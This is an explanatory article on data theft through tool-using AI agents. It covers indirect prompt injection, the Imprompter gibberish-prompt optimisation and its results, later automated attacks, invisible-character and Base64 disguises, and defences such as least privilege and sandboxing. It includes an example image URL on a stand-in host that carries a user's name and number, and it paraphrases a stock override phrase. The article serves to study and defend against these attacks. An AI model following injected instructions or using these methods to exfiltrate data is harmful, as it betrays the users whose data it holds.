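# Data theft through tool-using AI agents by disguised inputs, and the defences of least privilege, role isolation and sandboxing

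## How can an AI agent be made to send out private data?

An AI agent is a large language model, such as those behind ChatGPT and Claude, connected to software that carries out actions specified in the model's text. It can search the web, open files, send emails or run programs, and people now connect agents to their inboxes, calendars and company documents. An attacker who gets a few lines of text in front of an agent may cause it to collect private data and send it to a server the attacker controls. Security engineers call this kind of unauthorised transfer exfiltration. The attacker needs no stolen password, and the attack can succeed even when all the software involved works as its makers intended.

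The attacker's instruction may be in plain English, or it may be a disguised input, written as gibberish, invisible characters or encoded text that people and filters fail to recognise but the agent can still act on. Apart from who notices it, the attack works the same way in both cases, beginning with how the agent turns text into action.

### How text becomes action

Around the model sits the runtime, the software that spots the model's requests for action, executes them and returns the results. Fu, Li and colleagues (2024), in *Imprompter*, a paper on an attack with gibberish prompts, describe the cycle between the two. For a user who wants a summary of the day's email, it runs roughly like this:

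1. The runtime passes the user's request to the model, along with a description of the available tools.
2. The model writes a tool call, which is text in a fixed syntax that names a tool and fills in its parameters. Here it is a search of the inbox for today's messages.
3. The runtime, which scans the model's output continuously, detects the syntax, pauses the model and executes the search.
4. The runtime puts the messages into the model's context, the running text from which the model predicts what comes next, and the model continues.
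5. The model writes another tool call, and the cycle repeats, or it writes the answer that the user sees.

According to Anthropic's developer guide *How tool use works*, the model "never runs anything on its own". For many tools, the developer's program runs each call, so the developer can inspect it first. But Anthropic's servers run web searches and page fetches, often several in a row, and the developer usually learns of them only afterwards. A check in the developer's program would then come too late to stop the request.

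The syntax of tool calls varies by vendor. Fu and colleagues list calls that look like a line of Python, calls in JSON (a common format for structured data) and calls between XML-style tags. An attacker only has to know which format the target uses. Users don't see the calls, because the runtime hides them from the conversation. A well-formed call doesn't show whether the user or an attacker prompted it, so if an attacker's text leads the model to write one, a basic runtime executes it just as it would for the user.

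Chat products often give the model another tool, image rendering, though few people would think of it as one. Models format their answers in Markdown, a light notation in which a picture is written as an exclamation mark, a caption and a web address. When the model writes one, the chat page has the user's browser request the picture from that address. Fu and colleagues therefore count image rendering among an agent's tools. This seems right, because the model writes text in a fixed syntax and software outside the model responds by contacting a server, with the address the model composed as the parameter. Microsoft (2025), which has had to close this leak in its own products, notes that the browser makes the request without any action by the user.

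In April 2023, within months of ChatGPT's release, Roman Samoilenko demonstrated that a one-pixel Markdown image could carry data out of a chat. The software developer Simon Willison, who has collected dozens of such cases, described the method in *New prompt injection attack on ChatGPT web version* (2023). OpenAI did not start checking image addresses before display until that December, as Willison reported in *OpenAI Begins Tackling ChatGPT Data Leak Vulnerability* (2023).

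### What a web address carries

It may seem odd that fetching a picture can give anything away, since the data appears to flow towards the user. But the request itself travels outward, and it contains the address. Suppose a user called Ada Moreno has typed a name and phone number into a chat, and the model then writes an image with this invented address:

`https://pictures.example/Ada%20Moreno/logo.png?tel=5550142`

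Berners-Lee (2005), in *RFC 3986*, the standard for web addresses, divides such a string into parts:

| Part | Here | What it does |
| --- | --- | --- |
| Scheme | `https` | Sets the method of connection |
| Host | `pictures.example` | Picks the server that receives the request |
| Path | `/Ada%20Moreno/logo.png` | Names an item on that server; here it also holds the name, with `%20` standing for a space |
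| Query | `tel=5550142` | Adds further identifying data; here, the phone number |

Only the host in a URL has to be real. The receiving server interprets the path and query, so a sender can put any text there that uses permitted characters. If the attacker owns the host, the browser sends the name and number straight to the attacker. Encrypting the connection doesn't help, since the attacker's server is the intended recipient.

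The attacker doesn't need to write a program to catch the data either. According to Apache's *Log Files*, the manual page for a widely used web server, the access log records every request that the server processes. In the standard format each line holds the requesting computer's network address, the time, the request with its path and query, and a status code for the outcome. Ada Moreno's details would leave a line like this:

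`203.0.113.7 - - [12/Mar/2026:10:15:32 +0000] "GET /Ada%20Moreno/logo.png?tel=5550142 HTTP/1.1" 404 196`

The code 404 means that the server found no such item, but the server still receives and logs the address. In a real example from the University of Cambridge's course page *Access logs*, someone requested a nonexistent page called "nonsuch", and the log kept the full path next to the 404. So an attacker can collect names and numbers from the requested addresses even if the server holds no pictures. The one-pixel image is optional, but useful because a missing picture might leave a visible gap in the chat.

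The user may have little chance of noticing the leak, even by reading the agent's replies carefully. In OpenAI's *Keeping your data safe when an AI agent clicks a link* (2026), the engineers Adrian Spânu and Thomas Shadwell point out that the request can happen in the background, while an embedded image or link preview loads, and that the written answer need not contain anything sensitive.

Images are only one kind of outbound channel, meaning any action of an agent that can carry data to an outside party. Microsoft lists others. The model can write a link with the data in its address, which leaks when the user clicks. It can call a tool that publishes, such as one that writes to a public code repository. It can also use a covert channel, in which the content of the action doesn't matter. If an outsider can observe whether the agent called a certain tool, the call or its absence transmits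 only one bit, but that is enough to answer a yes-or-no question about, say, a planned merger. Images stand out because they make a zero-click attack possible, which needs nothing from the victim beyond ordinary use of the agent.

### Why the agent acts on a stranger's text

Attackers can use prompt injection to make the model compose such addresses without the user's request. Prompt injection is text from an attacker that the model treats as an instruction. Microsoft distinguishes direct prompt injection, in which the attacker is the user, from indirect prompt injection, in which the attacker inserts instructions into someone else's session, usually through content that the agent reads.

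*Not what you've signed up for* (Greshake, Endres and colleagues, 2023) introduced indirect prompt injection and catalogued ways to deliver it. An attacker can put the text on a web page and wait for an agent to retrieve it, or email it to someone whose assistant processes incoming mail. In the paper's tests of the chat sidebar in Microsoft's Edge browser, instructions on the open page took effect even though the user couldn't see them. The catalogue also includes text that victims paste in themselves, after copying it from the attacker's site or hearing that it does something clever. Although the user enters the text, this is still indirect by Microsoft's definition because the user is the victim. The gibberish prompts of *Imprompter* can reach people this way.

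In *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)*, which the UK's National Cyber Security Centre published in December 2025, David C describes a recruiter's system that tells a model to score CVs. One candidate hides a sentence in a CV telling the model to ignore its instructions and approve the candidate for interview. The model acts on that sentence as a command, although the recruiter meant the whole CV as data.

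The article's title refers to SQL injection, a similar but older attack. For years, attackers typed commands in SQL, a language for querying databases, into web forms that expected a name or a date, and careless websites ran them. Parameterised queries prevent this by passing the command and the user's entry to the database separately, so that the database engine cannot interpret the entry as a command, whatever it contains. David C argues that language models have no equivalent. A model receives a single sequence of tokens (words or fragments of words) and predicts the next one. The user's request, the developer's instructions and the stranger's email are all in that sequence, and no component enforces a boundary between them.

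Developers mark the boundaries between stretches of text with labels for each one's role, such as user, tool output or the model's own earlier words, and train models to give a user's words more authority than a web page's. In *Prompt Injection as Role Confusion*, Ye, Cui and Hadfield-Menell (2026) found that text that sounds like a user's registers inside the model as a user's, more or less regardless of its label. They wrapped identical passages of ordinary web text in each of five role labels and trained a simple classifier to tell from the model's internal activity which label was present. Because only the labels differed, the classifier could learn only their effect. They then relabelled real users' messages as tool output. If the labels had determined how the model represented the text, the classifier should have reported tool output almost every time. Across four models, it instead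 gave the messages an average probability of 76–88% of being a user's words, and never more than 20% of being tool output.

Ye and colleagues tested data theft by wrapping one fixed command, to send off a file, in 212 different framings, planting these in web pages and having an agent summarise the pages. Over 1,000 attempts, the agent sent the file 2% of the time in the group where the command registered least as a user's words, and 70% of the time where it registered most. The command's wording can't explain the gap because it never changed. The framings may affect compliance in other ways, but the relationship held when the researchers controlled for the role each framing claimed. The four models they probed are mid-sized, so the exact figures may not carry over to the largest commercial systems.

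These results slightly qualify David C's account. The classifier could learn the labels only because they leave some trace inside the model, so models do learn in training to distinguish instructions from data. But the distinction is a matter of degree, and an attacker's choice of words can outweigh it. Some researchers want to build it into the architecture instead. An ordinary model converts a token into the same list of numbers, its embedding, whether the token belongs to an instruction or to a document. *ASIDE* (2025) proposes rotating the embeddings of data so that they differ from those of instructions from the first step. Its models separate instructions from data better than ordinary ones do, but they don't guarantee the separation as a parameterised query does.

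In OpenAI's *Designing AI agents to resist prompt injection* (2026), Shadwell and Spânu report that most of the attacks they see on ChatGPT try to send secrets from a conversation to a third party, and that most of those they know of fail because the trained model refuses. But an attacker can send many emails, and Shadwell and Spânu describe one from 2025, written as a routine follow-up about staffing, that worked in half of all tests with one particular request from the user.

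People often confuse these attacks with jailbreaking, but Willison (2024) argues that the two are different. In a jailbreak, the user tries to get past the vendor's rules, for instance to obtain instructions for building a phishing site, whereas the attacks described here target an honest user's own data. Training a model to refuse dangerous topics does little to protect that user, because the attacks rely on ordinary actions, such as loading a picture or forwarding an email, that become theft only when an attacker requests them.

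### The three conditions for theft

The attacker needs only some text that the agent will read and, usually, a server that keeps a log. The attacker has no access to the victim's account, but the agent does, and it acts with the victim's permissions. Security engineers have long used the term "confused deputy" for a privileged program that an outsider can steer into misusing its privileges, and David C calls language models "inherently confusable".

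Willison (2025), in *The lethal trifecta for AI agents*, reduced the situation to three capabilities that are dangerous in combination:

- access to private data;
- exposure to untrusted content, meaning any text or image that an attacker could have influenced;
- a way to communicate outward.

An agent can be used for this theft only if it has access to private data, reads untrusted content that can carry the attacker's instructions, and has an outbound channel through which to send the data. OpenAI's engineers reason similarly when they look for a "source", through which an attacker can influence the system, and a "sink", an action that becomes dangerous in the wrong context.

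The conditions are easy to meet by accident. Ada Moreno's chat had no files or accounts connected to it, and the private data was what she had typed. A single email tool can meet all three conditions, since an inbox is private, anyone can write to it, and the tool may also send messages. Willison worries most about people who combine tools from different makers, because the combination can meet all three conditions even if no one maker has supplied them all. He acknowledges that the scheme covers only data theft. An agent with no way to send anything out could still delete files on a stranger's instruction.

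Its advantage is that it suggests defences that don't depend on anyone recognising the malicious text, which may be disguised. Least privilege gives an agent only the permissions its current task needs, which reduces the private data it can reach and the number of tools that could send that data out. Role isolation separates reading untrusted content from choosing actions, so that no part of the agent does both. A sandbox limits, from outside the model, which files, processes and network connections the agent's programs can use. It can also apply egress control, which restricts the destinations those programs may contact and what they may send there.

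## How did the Imprompter attack work, and how well?

Fu and colleagues illustrate the Imprompter attack with a job applicant who has been working on an application with a chat agent, so the conversation already contains a name, contact details and something about the job. The applicant finds a prompt online that looks like gibberish but supposedly helps with applications, and pastes it into the chat. The agent replies with an image whose address carries the applicant's details to the attacker's server.

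Fu and colleagues think some people would paste in text they can't read, because people already share prompts online and because prompts that a computer has tuned for harmless purposes can look just as strange. This is plausible, but they didn't test it on people. Their experiments start with the prompt already in the chat.

This way of leaking data was already known when the paper came out in October 2024, a year and a half after Samoilenko's one-pixel image. Willison (2024), in *This prompt can make an AI chatbot identify and extract personal details*, singled out the disguise as what was new. Earlier attackers had written their instructions in English, which a wary user could read before pasting.

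### What the attacker wanted and needed

Fu and colleagues wanted a prompt that hides its purpose from readers, makes the model write an exact tool call, and works on commercial products whose models the attacker can't inspect.

The hard part of the attack is getting the model to write the tool call. Most earlier work on computer-generated attack prompts dealt with jailbreaks, where the model only has to begin its answer with a fixed sentence of agreement. In a data theft, the correct output depends on the victim, but the attacker uses the same prompt for everyone. The model has to find each victim's details, such as Ada Moreno's name and number, and put them into a valid web address. If it gets a bracket wrong, the runtime treats the result as ordinary text and no data leaks.

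The attacker needs a model's weights, the numbers set in training that determine how the model responds, to search for such a prompt. Vendors of commercial agents usually keep these secret, so Fu and colleagues chose products whose makers also publish a related model. The French company Mistral runs the LeChat agent and publishes the 12-billion-parameter Mistral Nemo. The team behind the Chinese agent ChatGLM publishes the 9-billion-parameter GLM-4-9B. The researchers ran the search on the published models and then tried the resulting prompts on the products. They didn't know which models the products used, but assumed that they were close to the published ones.

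The two products are therefore favourable cases for the attacker. They also had to offer a tool that could contact any web address. Meta's assistant didn't qualify because its runtime removes every address the model writes, so Fu and colleagues built their own agent on Meta's open model Llama 3.1 70B.

### Searching for the prompt

The search needs a number that measures how close a candidate prompt is to working. Suppose the attacker has *m* sample conversations and has written out, for each one, the tool call that the model ought to produce. With *x* for the prompt, *c* for a conversation and *y* for the matching call, the number is:

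$$\mathcal{L}(x) = -\frac{1}{m}\sum_{j=1}^{m}\log P\left(y^{(j)} \mid c^{(j)}, x\right)$$

*P* is the probability that the model writes exactly that call after the conversation and the prompt. The negative logarithm turns a probability of 100% into a loss of 0, 50% into 0.69 and 1% into 4.6, so a lower loss is better for the attacker. Averaging the loss over many conversations favours a prompt that also works in chats the attacker has never seen.

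This loss treats all parts of the call alike, although a small slip in the syntax ruins everything. Fu and colleagues therefore added a second term:

$$\mathcal{L}_{joint} = \mathcal{L} + \lambda\,\mathcal{L}_{syn}$$

Here $\mathcal{L}_{syn}$ is the same average, computed only over the call's fixed opening, which is everything before the victim's own words. The weight λ sets how much this term counts, and it ranged from 0 to 1 across runs. With λ at 0, two prompts for ChatGLM's browser tool still reached 87% and 92% correct calls on the open model, so the extra term wasn't always necessary.

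The sample conversations came from collections of real chats. For the attack that extracts keywords, the researchers took 100 conversations with ChatGPT and had the target model list the keywords in each. This made the search easier, because the prompt only had to bring out words that the model would pick anyway. For the attack that extracts personal data, they used 24 conversations about job, visa and other applications. They replaced redacted details with invented ones and marked by hand what counted as personal.

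A computer can't adjust a prompt as it would a picture, by making each pixel slightly lighter, because there is nothing halfway between two tokens. Trying every possible swap is also hopeless. With a prompt of 50 tokens and a vocabulary of 100,000, choosing a single change would take five million test runs. Fu and colleagues adapted greedy coordinate gradient search (GCG), which Andy Zou and colleagues had published in 2023 for jailbreaks. Each round goes roughly like this:

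1. The program uses the weights to compute a gradient, which gives a rough estimate of how much each possible token would lower the loss at each position.
2. It keeps the most promising tokens for each position, 256 in this study, and picks a few of them at random.
3. It runs the model on each candidate to measure the actual loss.
4. It keeps the best candidate and starts the next round from there.

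The search is called "greedy" because it makes the best swap at each step without accounting for later steps. The search took 6 to 44 hours per prompt, and a single graphics card was enough for the two smaller models.

GCG for jailbreaks usually starts from a row of exclamation marks. According to Fu and colleagues, a search for prompts that trigger working tool calls has almost no chance of success from that starting point, so they started from a plain-language version of the instruction, lengthened with scattered punctuation marks. But a search that starts from English may also end with readable English, which the loss does not penalise.

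One remedy was a vocabulary mask, which removes English words from the permitted replacements, so the search has to use words from other languages and special characters. Willison points out that this works because models are multilingual, so tokens from several languages can have the same effect as the English original. Only one of the five optimised prompts that Fu and colleagues tried on real products used the mask. They instead produced their best prompt for personal data by taking an earlier result that was still too readable, replacing the telltale words with punctuation and running the search again.

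The researchers measured the disguise by its perplexity, which is high when a text is hard for a language model to predict. Ordinary English scores below 10 on the model they used, and the best prompt for extracting personal data scored 7,489. However, a filter could use such a high score to detect the prompt. The example that Willison reprints also still contains several English words and the attacker's domain name, so a careful reader could become suspicious without working out what the text does.

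Fu and colleagues also hid instructions in pictures. This is easier than with text, because pixel values can change by tiny amounts, so standard gradient methods work directly. People also can't tell by looking at a picture how it will affect a model. They altered six images and tested them on PaliGemma, a small open model from Google that accepts images. The model wrote a correct tool call in 82–88% of cases. The added noise was visible in some pictures but hard to spot in a photograph of doughnuts with dotted frosting. Fu and colleagues found no commercial agent that met their criteria for this variant, so its success on real products remains unknown.

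### What leaked from LeChat and ChatGLM

Fu and colleagues tested the keyword attack on 100 conversations that the search had not used. They ran each conversation three times on the open models. LeChat and ChatGLM allowed only about 35 of these conversations a day, so the product tests made one attempt per conversation. They covered 98 conversations because two were flagged as harmful. The attack on personal data was tested on 25 conversations, which contained an average of 7.4 personal details each.

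They counted a call as correct if the reply contained text in exactly the required syntax. Precision is the share of extracted terms that came from the conversation or, in the second attack, were personal data. Recall is the share of the personal data in the conversation that ended up in the address. The labels T1 to T12 are the researchers' own. The last column below multiplies the share of correct calls by recall to give the share of a victim's personal data that an attacker could expect from one attempt.

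| Product and prompt | Target | Correct calls | Precision | Recall | Expected share per attempt |
| --- | --- | --- | --- | --- | --- |
| LeChat, T1 | Keywords | 84.7% | 70.1% | – | – |
| ChatGLM, T5 | Keywords | 99.0% | 62.5% | – | – |
| LeChat, T10 | Personal data | 100% | 70.4% | 41.2% | 41% |
| LeChat, plain language | Personal data | 44.0% | 80.2% | 48.2% | 21% |
| ChatGLM, T11 | Personal data | 96.0% | 0% | 0% | 0% |
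| ChatGLM, T12 | Personal data | 92.0% | 34.7% | 63.0% | 58% |
| ChatGLM, plain language | Personal data | 40.0% | 89.1% | 48.1% | 19% |

On LeChat, the disguised prompt T10 would get the attacker about 41% of the personal data per attempt, compared with about 21% for the hand-written prompt in plain language. T10 always produced a correct call. The plain prompt did so in only 44.0% of conversations, and those calls carried 48.2% of the personal data on average. The plain prompt has higher precision and recall, but both measures leave out every attempt without a correct call.

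T10's advantage doesn't show that gibberish is inherently more effective than English, because T10 came from many hours of automated search and was compared with a single hand-written prompt. A fairer comparison would put the same effort into a readable prompt. On the open models, the advantage over hand-written prompts also varied widely. In the keyword attack on Llama 3.1 70B, the disguised prompts produced correct tool calls 79–82% of the time and the hand-written one 72%. On GLM-4, with images as the outbound channel, the disguised prompts succeeded in 84–90% of cases and the hand-written prompt never worked.

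The rate of correct calls alone is a poor measure of theft. On ChatGLM, T11 produced a correct call in 96% of conversations but stole nothing, because the address always contained the same single term from the attacker's own prompt. On the open GLM-4 model, the same prompt had extracted 22% of the personal data in its correct calls. T12 had higher recall on the product than on the open model, at 63% compared with 17%. Fu and colleagues suspect that ChatGLM runs a much larger and quite different model from the one they used to search for prompts. An attacker who can't test a prompt on the product may therefore have little idea what it will do there.

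T10 is less precise when there is no personal data to find. In the 98 general conversations, LeChat still wrote a correct call 90.8% of the time, but only 41.8% of the extracted words came from the conversation. When the attacks failed altogether, the agents mostly listed the keywords as plain text in the chat, which would have given the user a hint. Occasionally they wrote the correct call inside a code block, which the chat page displays without executing.

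The samples are small, especially for personal data. The difference between 11 and 25 correct calls out of 25 is too large to be chance, but a perfect score doesn't show that the attack always works, because a prompt that works 89% of the time would still get 25 out of 25 in about one in twenty such tests. The researchers had also used the same conversations to pick the best prompt from each batch, which probably inflates the results a little, although they did this on the open models. The "nearly 80%" success rate in the paper's abstract matches T10's precision on the open model, 79.8%, while its precision on LeChat was 70.4%.

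### Mistral's fix

Fu and colleagues reported the attack to Mistral on 9 September 2024. Mistral rated it medium severity and on 13 September stopped LeChat from displaying images from external addresses, which in effect removed a permission. The researchers confirmed that the fix worked. The model could presumably still write the same text, but the chat page no longer loaded the image, so disguising the prompt did not help the attack.

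The researchers told the ChatGLM team on 18 September and got a reply only after several attempts through various channels. When the paper appeared, the team had just begun work on the problem. Bitdefender, a security company, reported at the time that there was no evidence that anyone had used the technique to steal data from real users.

Blocking images stopped one way of leaking data from LeChat. 0DIN's *Mistral LeChat Data Exfiltration via Email Embedded Indirect Prompt Injection* describes another leak, in which instructions in an email caused LeChat to encode conversation data and send it to the attacker's addresses.

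### Searching without the weights

Imprompter depends on a published model that resembles the product. Fu and colleagues expected a direct attack on a closed model to be extremely difficult because their search relied on gradients. Researchers have since found several ways to search without gradients. *The Resurgence of GCG Adversarial Attacks on Large Language Models* (2025) lists successors to the original GCG algorithm, including some that are faster, some that transfer better and some that only need to query the target.

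Google let developers fine-tune its closed Gemini models, which means training them further on the developer's own examples. The service reported a training loss for those examples, a measure of how far the model was from producing the desired output. In early 2025, Labunets, Pandya and colleagues, a group that included two of Imprompter's creators, found in *Fun-tuning* that this loss was close enough to the quantity Imprompter minimises to be a usable substitute. They set the learning rate so low that training barely changed the model, then submitted a thousand candidate prompts at a time and collected the losses. Google returned these in shuffled order, but the shuffle was the same for every batch of a given size, so they could work out most of it and reuse the result.

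The researchers tested the method on 40 injections from PurpleLlama, a public set of security tests. Without optimisation, the injections succeeded 27.5% of the time on Gemini 1.5 Flash and 42.5% on Gemini 1.0 Pro. Optimisation raised these rates to 65.3% and 82.0%. The whole experiment cost less than $10, though each prompt took about 15 hours on 1.0 Pro and 60 on 1.5 Flash.

In a control experiment, Labunets and colleagues replaced the losses with random numbers, which left the search without guidance, and still reached 43.8% and 61.3%. Almost half of the improvement over the original injections therefore came from something other than the fine-tuning signal. One likely reason is that each injection's score was its best result over 45 rounds, and with that many variations some will work by luck.

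*Fun-tuning* also solves a different problem from Imprompter. It places optimised tokens before and after an instruction that remains in readable English. Its attacks changed the model's answers, for instance by making it misstate what a piece of code does or direct the user to a phishing site, but they didn't have to produce a tool call containing private data. The study therefore shows that keeping a model's weights secret protects it less than it seems to, but it doesn't show that an attacker could have built T10 this way.

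Labunets and colleagues reported the leak to Google in November 2024. In early April 2025, Google restricted the service so that developers could no longer use tiny learning rates or match losses to individual examples. This closes that particular leak but gives developers less fine control over training.

A more general approach is to train a second model to write the attacks. In *The Attacker Moves Second* (2025), this model sends a candidate text to the target, receives a score, analyses the result and tries again. Reinforcement learning then trains the model by rewarding successful attempts, which makes similar ones more likely. The method requires access to the target and a way to tell whether an attempt worked, but not the target's weights.

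The difficulty is that almost every early attempt fails, and a long series of zeros gives the attacker nothing to learn from. Chen, Zhang and Tramèr (2026), in *Learning to Inject*, addressed this by having another model judge which of two failed attempts came closer to success. They trained an attacker with only 1.5 billion parameters and allowed it up to 260 queries for each task. Their tests used AgentDojo, a benchmark in which agents handle simulated email, banking, travel and workplace chat while an attacker tries to divert them. This is how it compared with the best of six hand-written attack templates:

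| Target model | Best template | Trained attacker |
| --- | --- | --- |
| Gemini 2.5 Flash | 23.6% | 58.0% |
| GPT-4.1-nano | 20.5% | 48.0% |
| Claude 3.5 Sonnet | 5.7% | 12.6% |
| GPT-5-nano | 1.6% | 11.5% |

The Claude figure covers banking tasks only, and the service the researchers used to reach the model added its own filter. Part of the general advantage comes from repeated tries, since the trained attacker can practise each task on the target, unlike the templates. Training adds a further advantage. On GPT-5-nano's banking tasks, the full method succeeded 36.6% of the time, compared with 17.4% for the same small model without training or the judge's comparisons.

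The attacker here also earned a reward when the agent finished the user's original task. This helps conceal the attack, because a victim who receives the requested work has less reason to suspect anything. The text itself was not well hidden, because the optimised part came after a plain instruction.

### Transfer to newer models

An attacker who can't query the victim's agent has to prepare the prompt on one model and hope that it works on another. Hofer, Debenedetti and Tramèr (2026), in *Assessing Automated Prompt Injection Attacks in Agentic Environments*, tested how well GCG prompts transfer between models. They ran the search on Qwen3-4B, a small open model from Alibaba, kept injections that worked, and tried them on seven other models. The injections succeeded in about 22–36% of attempts on three larger Qwen models, but in under 2% on GPT-5, GPT-5-mini and Claude Sonnet 4.5. On Gemini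 2.5 Flash, injections optimised across many tasks succeeded in 7.7% of attempts.

Imprompter succeeded on products that Fu and colleagues had deliberately chosen for having a close open-weight relative, and attacks often transfer within a model family. The method is unlikely to work on a product without such a relative. However, Hofer and colleagues' test differed from Imprompter in two ways. They left the attacker's goal readable, and they optimised for a sentence of agreement because this worked better in their setting than optimising for the exact tool call. They also note that searching on several source models at once might improve transfer.

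The gradient contributed little even on the model it came from. When Hofer and colleagues proposed replacement tokens at random and changed nothing else, the attack succeeded about 33% of the time, compared with about 25% for the normal, gradient-guided version. The test covered two of the benchmark's four areas, so the random version may not really be better, but there is no sign that gradients help. Together with the random control in *Fun-tuning*, this suggests that such attacks work largely because they try many variations. Hofer and colleagues also report that *The Attacker Moves Second* found gradient methods the least effective of those it compared.

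Prompts from trained attackers transfer unevenly too. Chen and colleagues optimised strings on GPT-5-nano and reused them on other models. With one fixed goal across 16 banking tasks, the strings succeeded 45.0% of the time on GPT-4o-mini but only 1.7% on Gemini 2.5 Flash. On a different set of eight tasks, the rate for Gemini 2.5 Flash was 55.8%. Transfer rates between the same two models can therefore vary widely with the tasks and the strings.

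The software around the model also affects how well an attack transfers. *Trojan Hippo Bench* (2026) tests attacks that persist in an agent's long-term memory, using prompts optimised for GPT-5-mini and reused unchanged on GPT-5. When the agent retrieved old text by searching for it, the success rate fell only from 80% on GPT-5-mini to 70% on GPT-5. With Mem0, a different memory system, it fell from 85% to zero. The study attributes such drops to memory systems that need more precisely formatted injections. A low transfer rate may therefore be a poor guide to how often attacks would succeed if the attacker could optimise them on the target itself.

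OpenAI has trained an attacker on a far larger scale. *GPT-Red* (Wallace, Choquette-Choo and colleagues, 2026) describes a model that learned by attacking a varied group of defending models while they learned to resist. The attacker reliably broke OpenAI's models up to GPT-5.5 and found more successful attacks than human testers had in a public competition. OpenAI then used it to train GPT-5.6, which Wallace and colleagues call their most robust model against prompt injection so far.

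Two months later, *Climbing the Hill* (2026) reported results against two models of the GPT-5.6 family. Training the attacker on GPT-5.6-Terra raised its success rate within ten attempts from 6.1% to 45.0%. The researchers couldn't afford to train on GPT-5.6-Sol, the most robust of the family, so they used the attacker from Terra unchanged. It succeeded in 2.9% of cases on the first attempt and 7.3% within ten, although the ten-attempt rate was 16.7% on tasks involving the code platform GitHub. The hardened models are therefore still vulnerable to an attacker that can train on them, and Sol's low figures are for an attacker that had not trained on it.

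The attacking model does not need to be large. *Heads of Security* (2026) trained attackers from an open model with 8 billion parameters on 310 example cases, and trained one of the attackers partly against GPT-5.6-Luna through an ordinary commercial interface.

Optimised prompts can therefore still work on recent models, but the successful ones tend to look quite different from Imprompter's gibberish. Besides GCG, Hofer and colleagues tested a method in which GPT-5 writes readable attacks and improves them after each failure. It succeeded about 45% of the time on Qwen3-4B and just under 5% on GPT-5, well ahead of GCG on both. Blunt commands that claimed special authority often worked on Qwen3-4B but mostly failed on GPT-5, which ignored them or asked the user for clarification. The injections that succeeded on GPT-5 looked like ordinary content, such as a bill whose payment details included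 the attacker's account. GPT-5 remarked that the account number looked unusual and asked for confirmation, but still included the details in its plan.

In one simulated theft, GPT-Red wrote a search result that imitated the defending model's reasoning, including an invented policy and a command to send off the user's data. The defending model referred to this text as if it were its own earlier reasoning and ran the command.

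## What other disguises exist, and do they help the attacker?

The gibberish in *Imprompter* came from hours of automated search, but most other disguises need none. The attacker writes a readable instruction and converts it by a fixed rule, such as replacing every letter with an invisible character. Anyone who knows the rule can recover the instruction.

Disguises differ in whom they deceive and in what recovers the instruction:

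| Disguise | Whom it deceives | What recovers the instruction |
| --- | --- | --- |
| White text on a white page | The user | Nothing has to, since the model receives ordinary text |
| Invisible characters | The user, and filters that search for suspicious words | The model itself or, more reliably, its code tool |
| Base64 and similar encodings | The user, and simple filters | The model itself or its code tool |
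| Text that appears when an image shrinks | The user | The software that resizes images for the model |
| Encryption | The user, and filters that only classify text | The code tool |
| A theft worded as a routine technical step | The model's own caution | Nothing has to |

A code tool lets the model write and run a short program, usually in Python, so it can decode text it couldn't work out by itself.

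Wording a theft as routine work disguises it by hiding the purpose of the instruction, even though the text stays in plain English. The experiments below suggest that hiding the purpose affects the model more than changing how the letters look.

### Invisible characters

Unicode, the standard that assigns a number to each character of text, includes some characters that take up no space on the screen. They have legitimate uses, such as joining several emoji into a single picture. An attacker can scatter these invisible characters through a visible sentence to hide certain words from a filter that searches for them, or use the characters to spell out a whole message that the user never sees.

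In *Reverse CAPTCHA*, Graves (2026) tested two ways of encoding whole hidden messages. The first converts each character's code to eight binary digits. The letter R, for example, has the code 82, which is 01010010 in binary. Each 0 is then written as a zero-width space and each 1 as a zero-width non-joiner, both of which are invisible. The harmless instruction "Reply VIOLET" has 12 characters, including the space, so it becomes 96 invisible ones.

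The second scheme uses Unicode's tag characters, an obsolete set with an invisible counterpart for every basic letter, digit and punctuation mark. The counterparts are in the same order, so a program can convert text by adding a constant to each character's number. R, which is 52 in hexadecimal, becomes E0052. "Reply VIOLET" becomes 12 tag characters. In both schemes the surrounding text looks unchanged on screen.

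Graves hid such instructions in 30 trivia questions. Each hidden instruction named a wrong answer, so the model's reply revealed whether it had followed the visible question or the hidden text. The study covered five models from OpenAI and Anthropic, with and without a Python tool, and produced 8,308 graded outputs. These are the shares in which the model gave only the hidden answer:

| Model | Without code tool | With code tool |
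| --- | --- | --- |
| Claude Sonnet 4 | 16.9% | 71.2% |
| Claude Opus 4 | 6.7% | 51.1% |
| Claude Haiku 4.5 | 0.8% | 49.2% |
| GPT-5.2 | 0.1% | 20.6% |
| GPT-4o-mini | 0.1% | 1.6% |

When the model followed the hidden text, its reply typically contained a few lines of code that converted the characters back. With the tool, the model only has to write a simple program instead of working out 96 binary digits by predicting tokens.

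The danger to an ordinary user is smaller than these figures suggest, because in three of the four test conditions the system prompt (the developer's standing instructions) told the model about the hidden text, either by naming the characters or by giving the full rule for decoding them. With these hints and the code tool, Claude Opus 4 followed every instruction written in tag characters. With the tool but no hints, the models followed the hidden text in 0–11% of cases, and with neither, in at most 1.1%.

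Someone who can only plant text on a web page can't write the system prompt. Graves therefore treats the high rates as measuring what models can decode when prompted, and the low rates as measuring how readily they do it unprompted. An attacker who controls the description of a tool or plug-in might supply the hints, since the runtime also puts such descriptions into the model's context.

The most effective encoding for an attacker depends on the vendor. With hints and the tool, GPT-5.2 followed 69–70% of the instructions in zero-width binary and almost none in tag characters. Claude Opus 4 followed 48–68% of those in zero-width binary and a higher share of those in tag characters. Graves suspects that the vendors' software that splits text into tokens treats the characters differently, but didn't inspect it. The difference offers little protection, because an attacker can put both versions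 on the same page.

A model that decodes the text also may not obey it. In some tests the hidden message began with a stock phrase of prompt injection, telling the model to ignore its previous instructions. Compliance was lower with this phrase than with neutral wording for Claude Opus 4 (23.9% compared with 32.0%) and GPT-5.2 (6.1% compared with 11.8%), even though the phrase always came with the full decoding rule. Claude Sonnet 4's compliance rose from 43.7% with neutral wording to 59.6% with the stock phrase, but the extra help with decoding may explain some of that rise.

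In all of these tests, the model only had to output a single harmless word. To steal data, an attacker needs the model to find private data and make a tool call, which gives the model more chances to fail or refuse. The study shows that the invisible channel works, particularly for agents that can run code, but not how often an attacker could steal data through it.

### Base64 and other simple encodings

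Base64 is a way of writing any data with 64 ordinary characters. Email programs use it to send attachments through systems built for text. The conversion splits the data's binary digits into groups of six and assigns a character to each group. The name "Ada", for example, becomes "QWRh". The conversion uses no key, so any programmer can reverse it in seconds.

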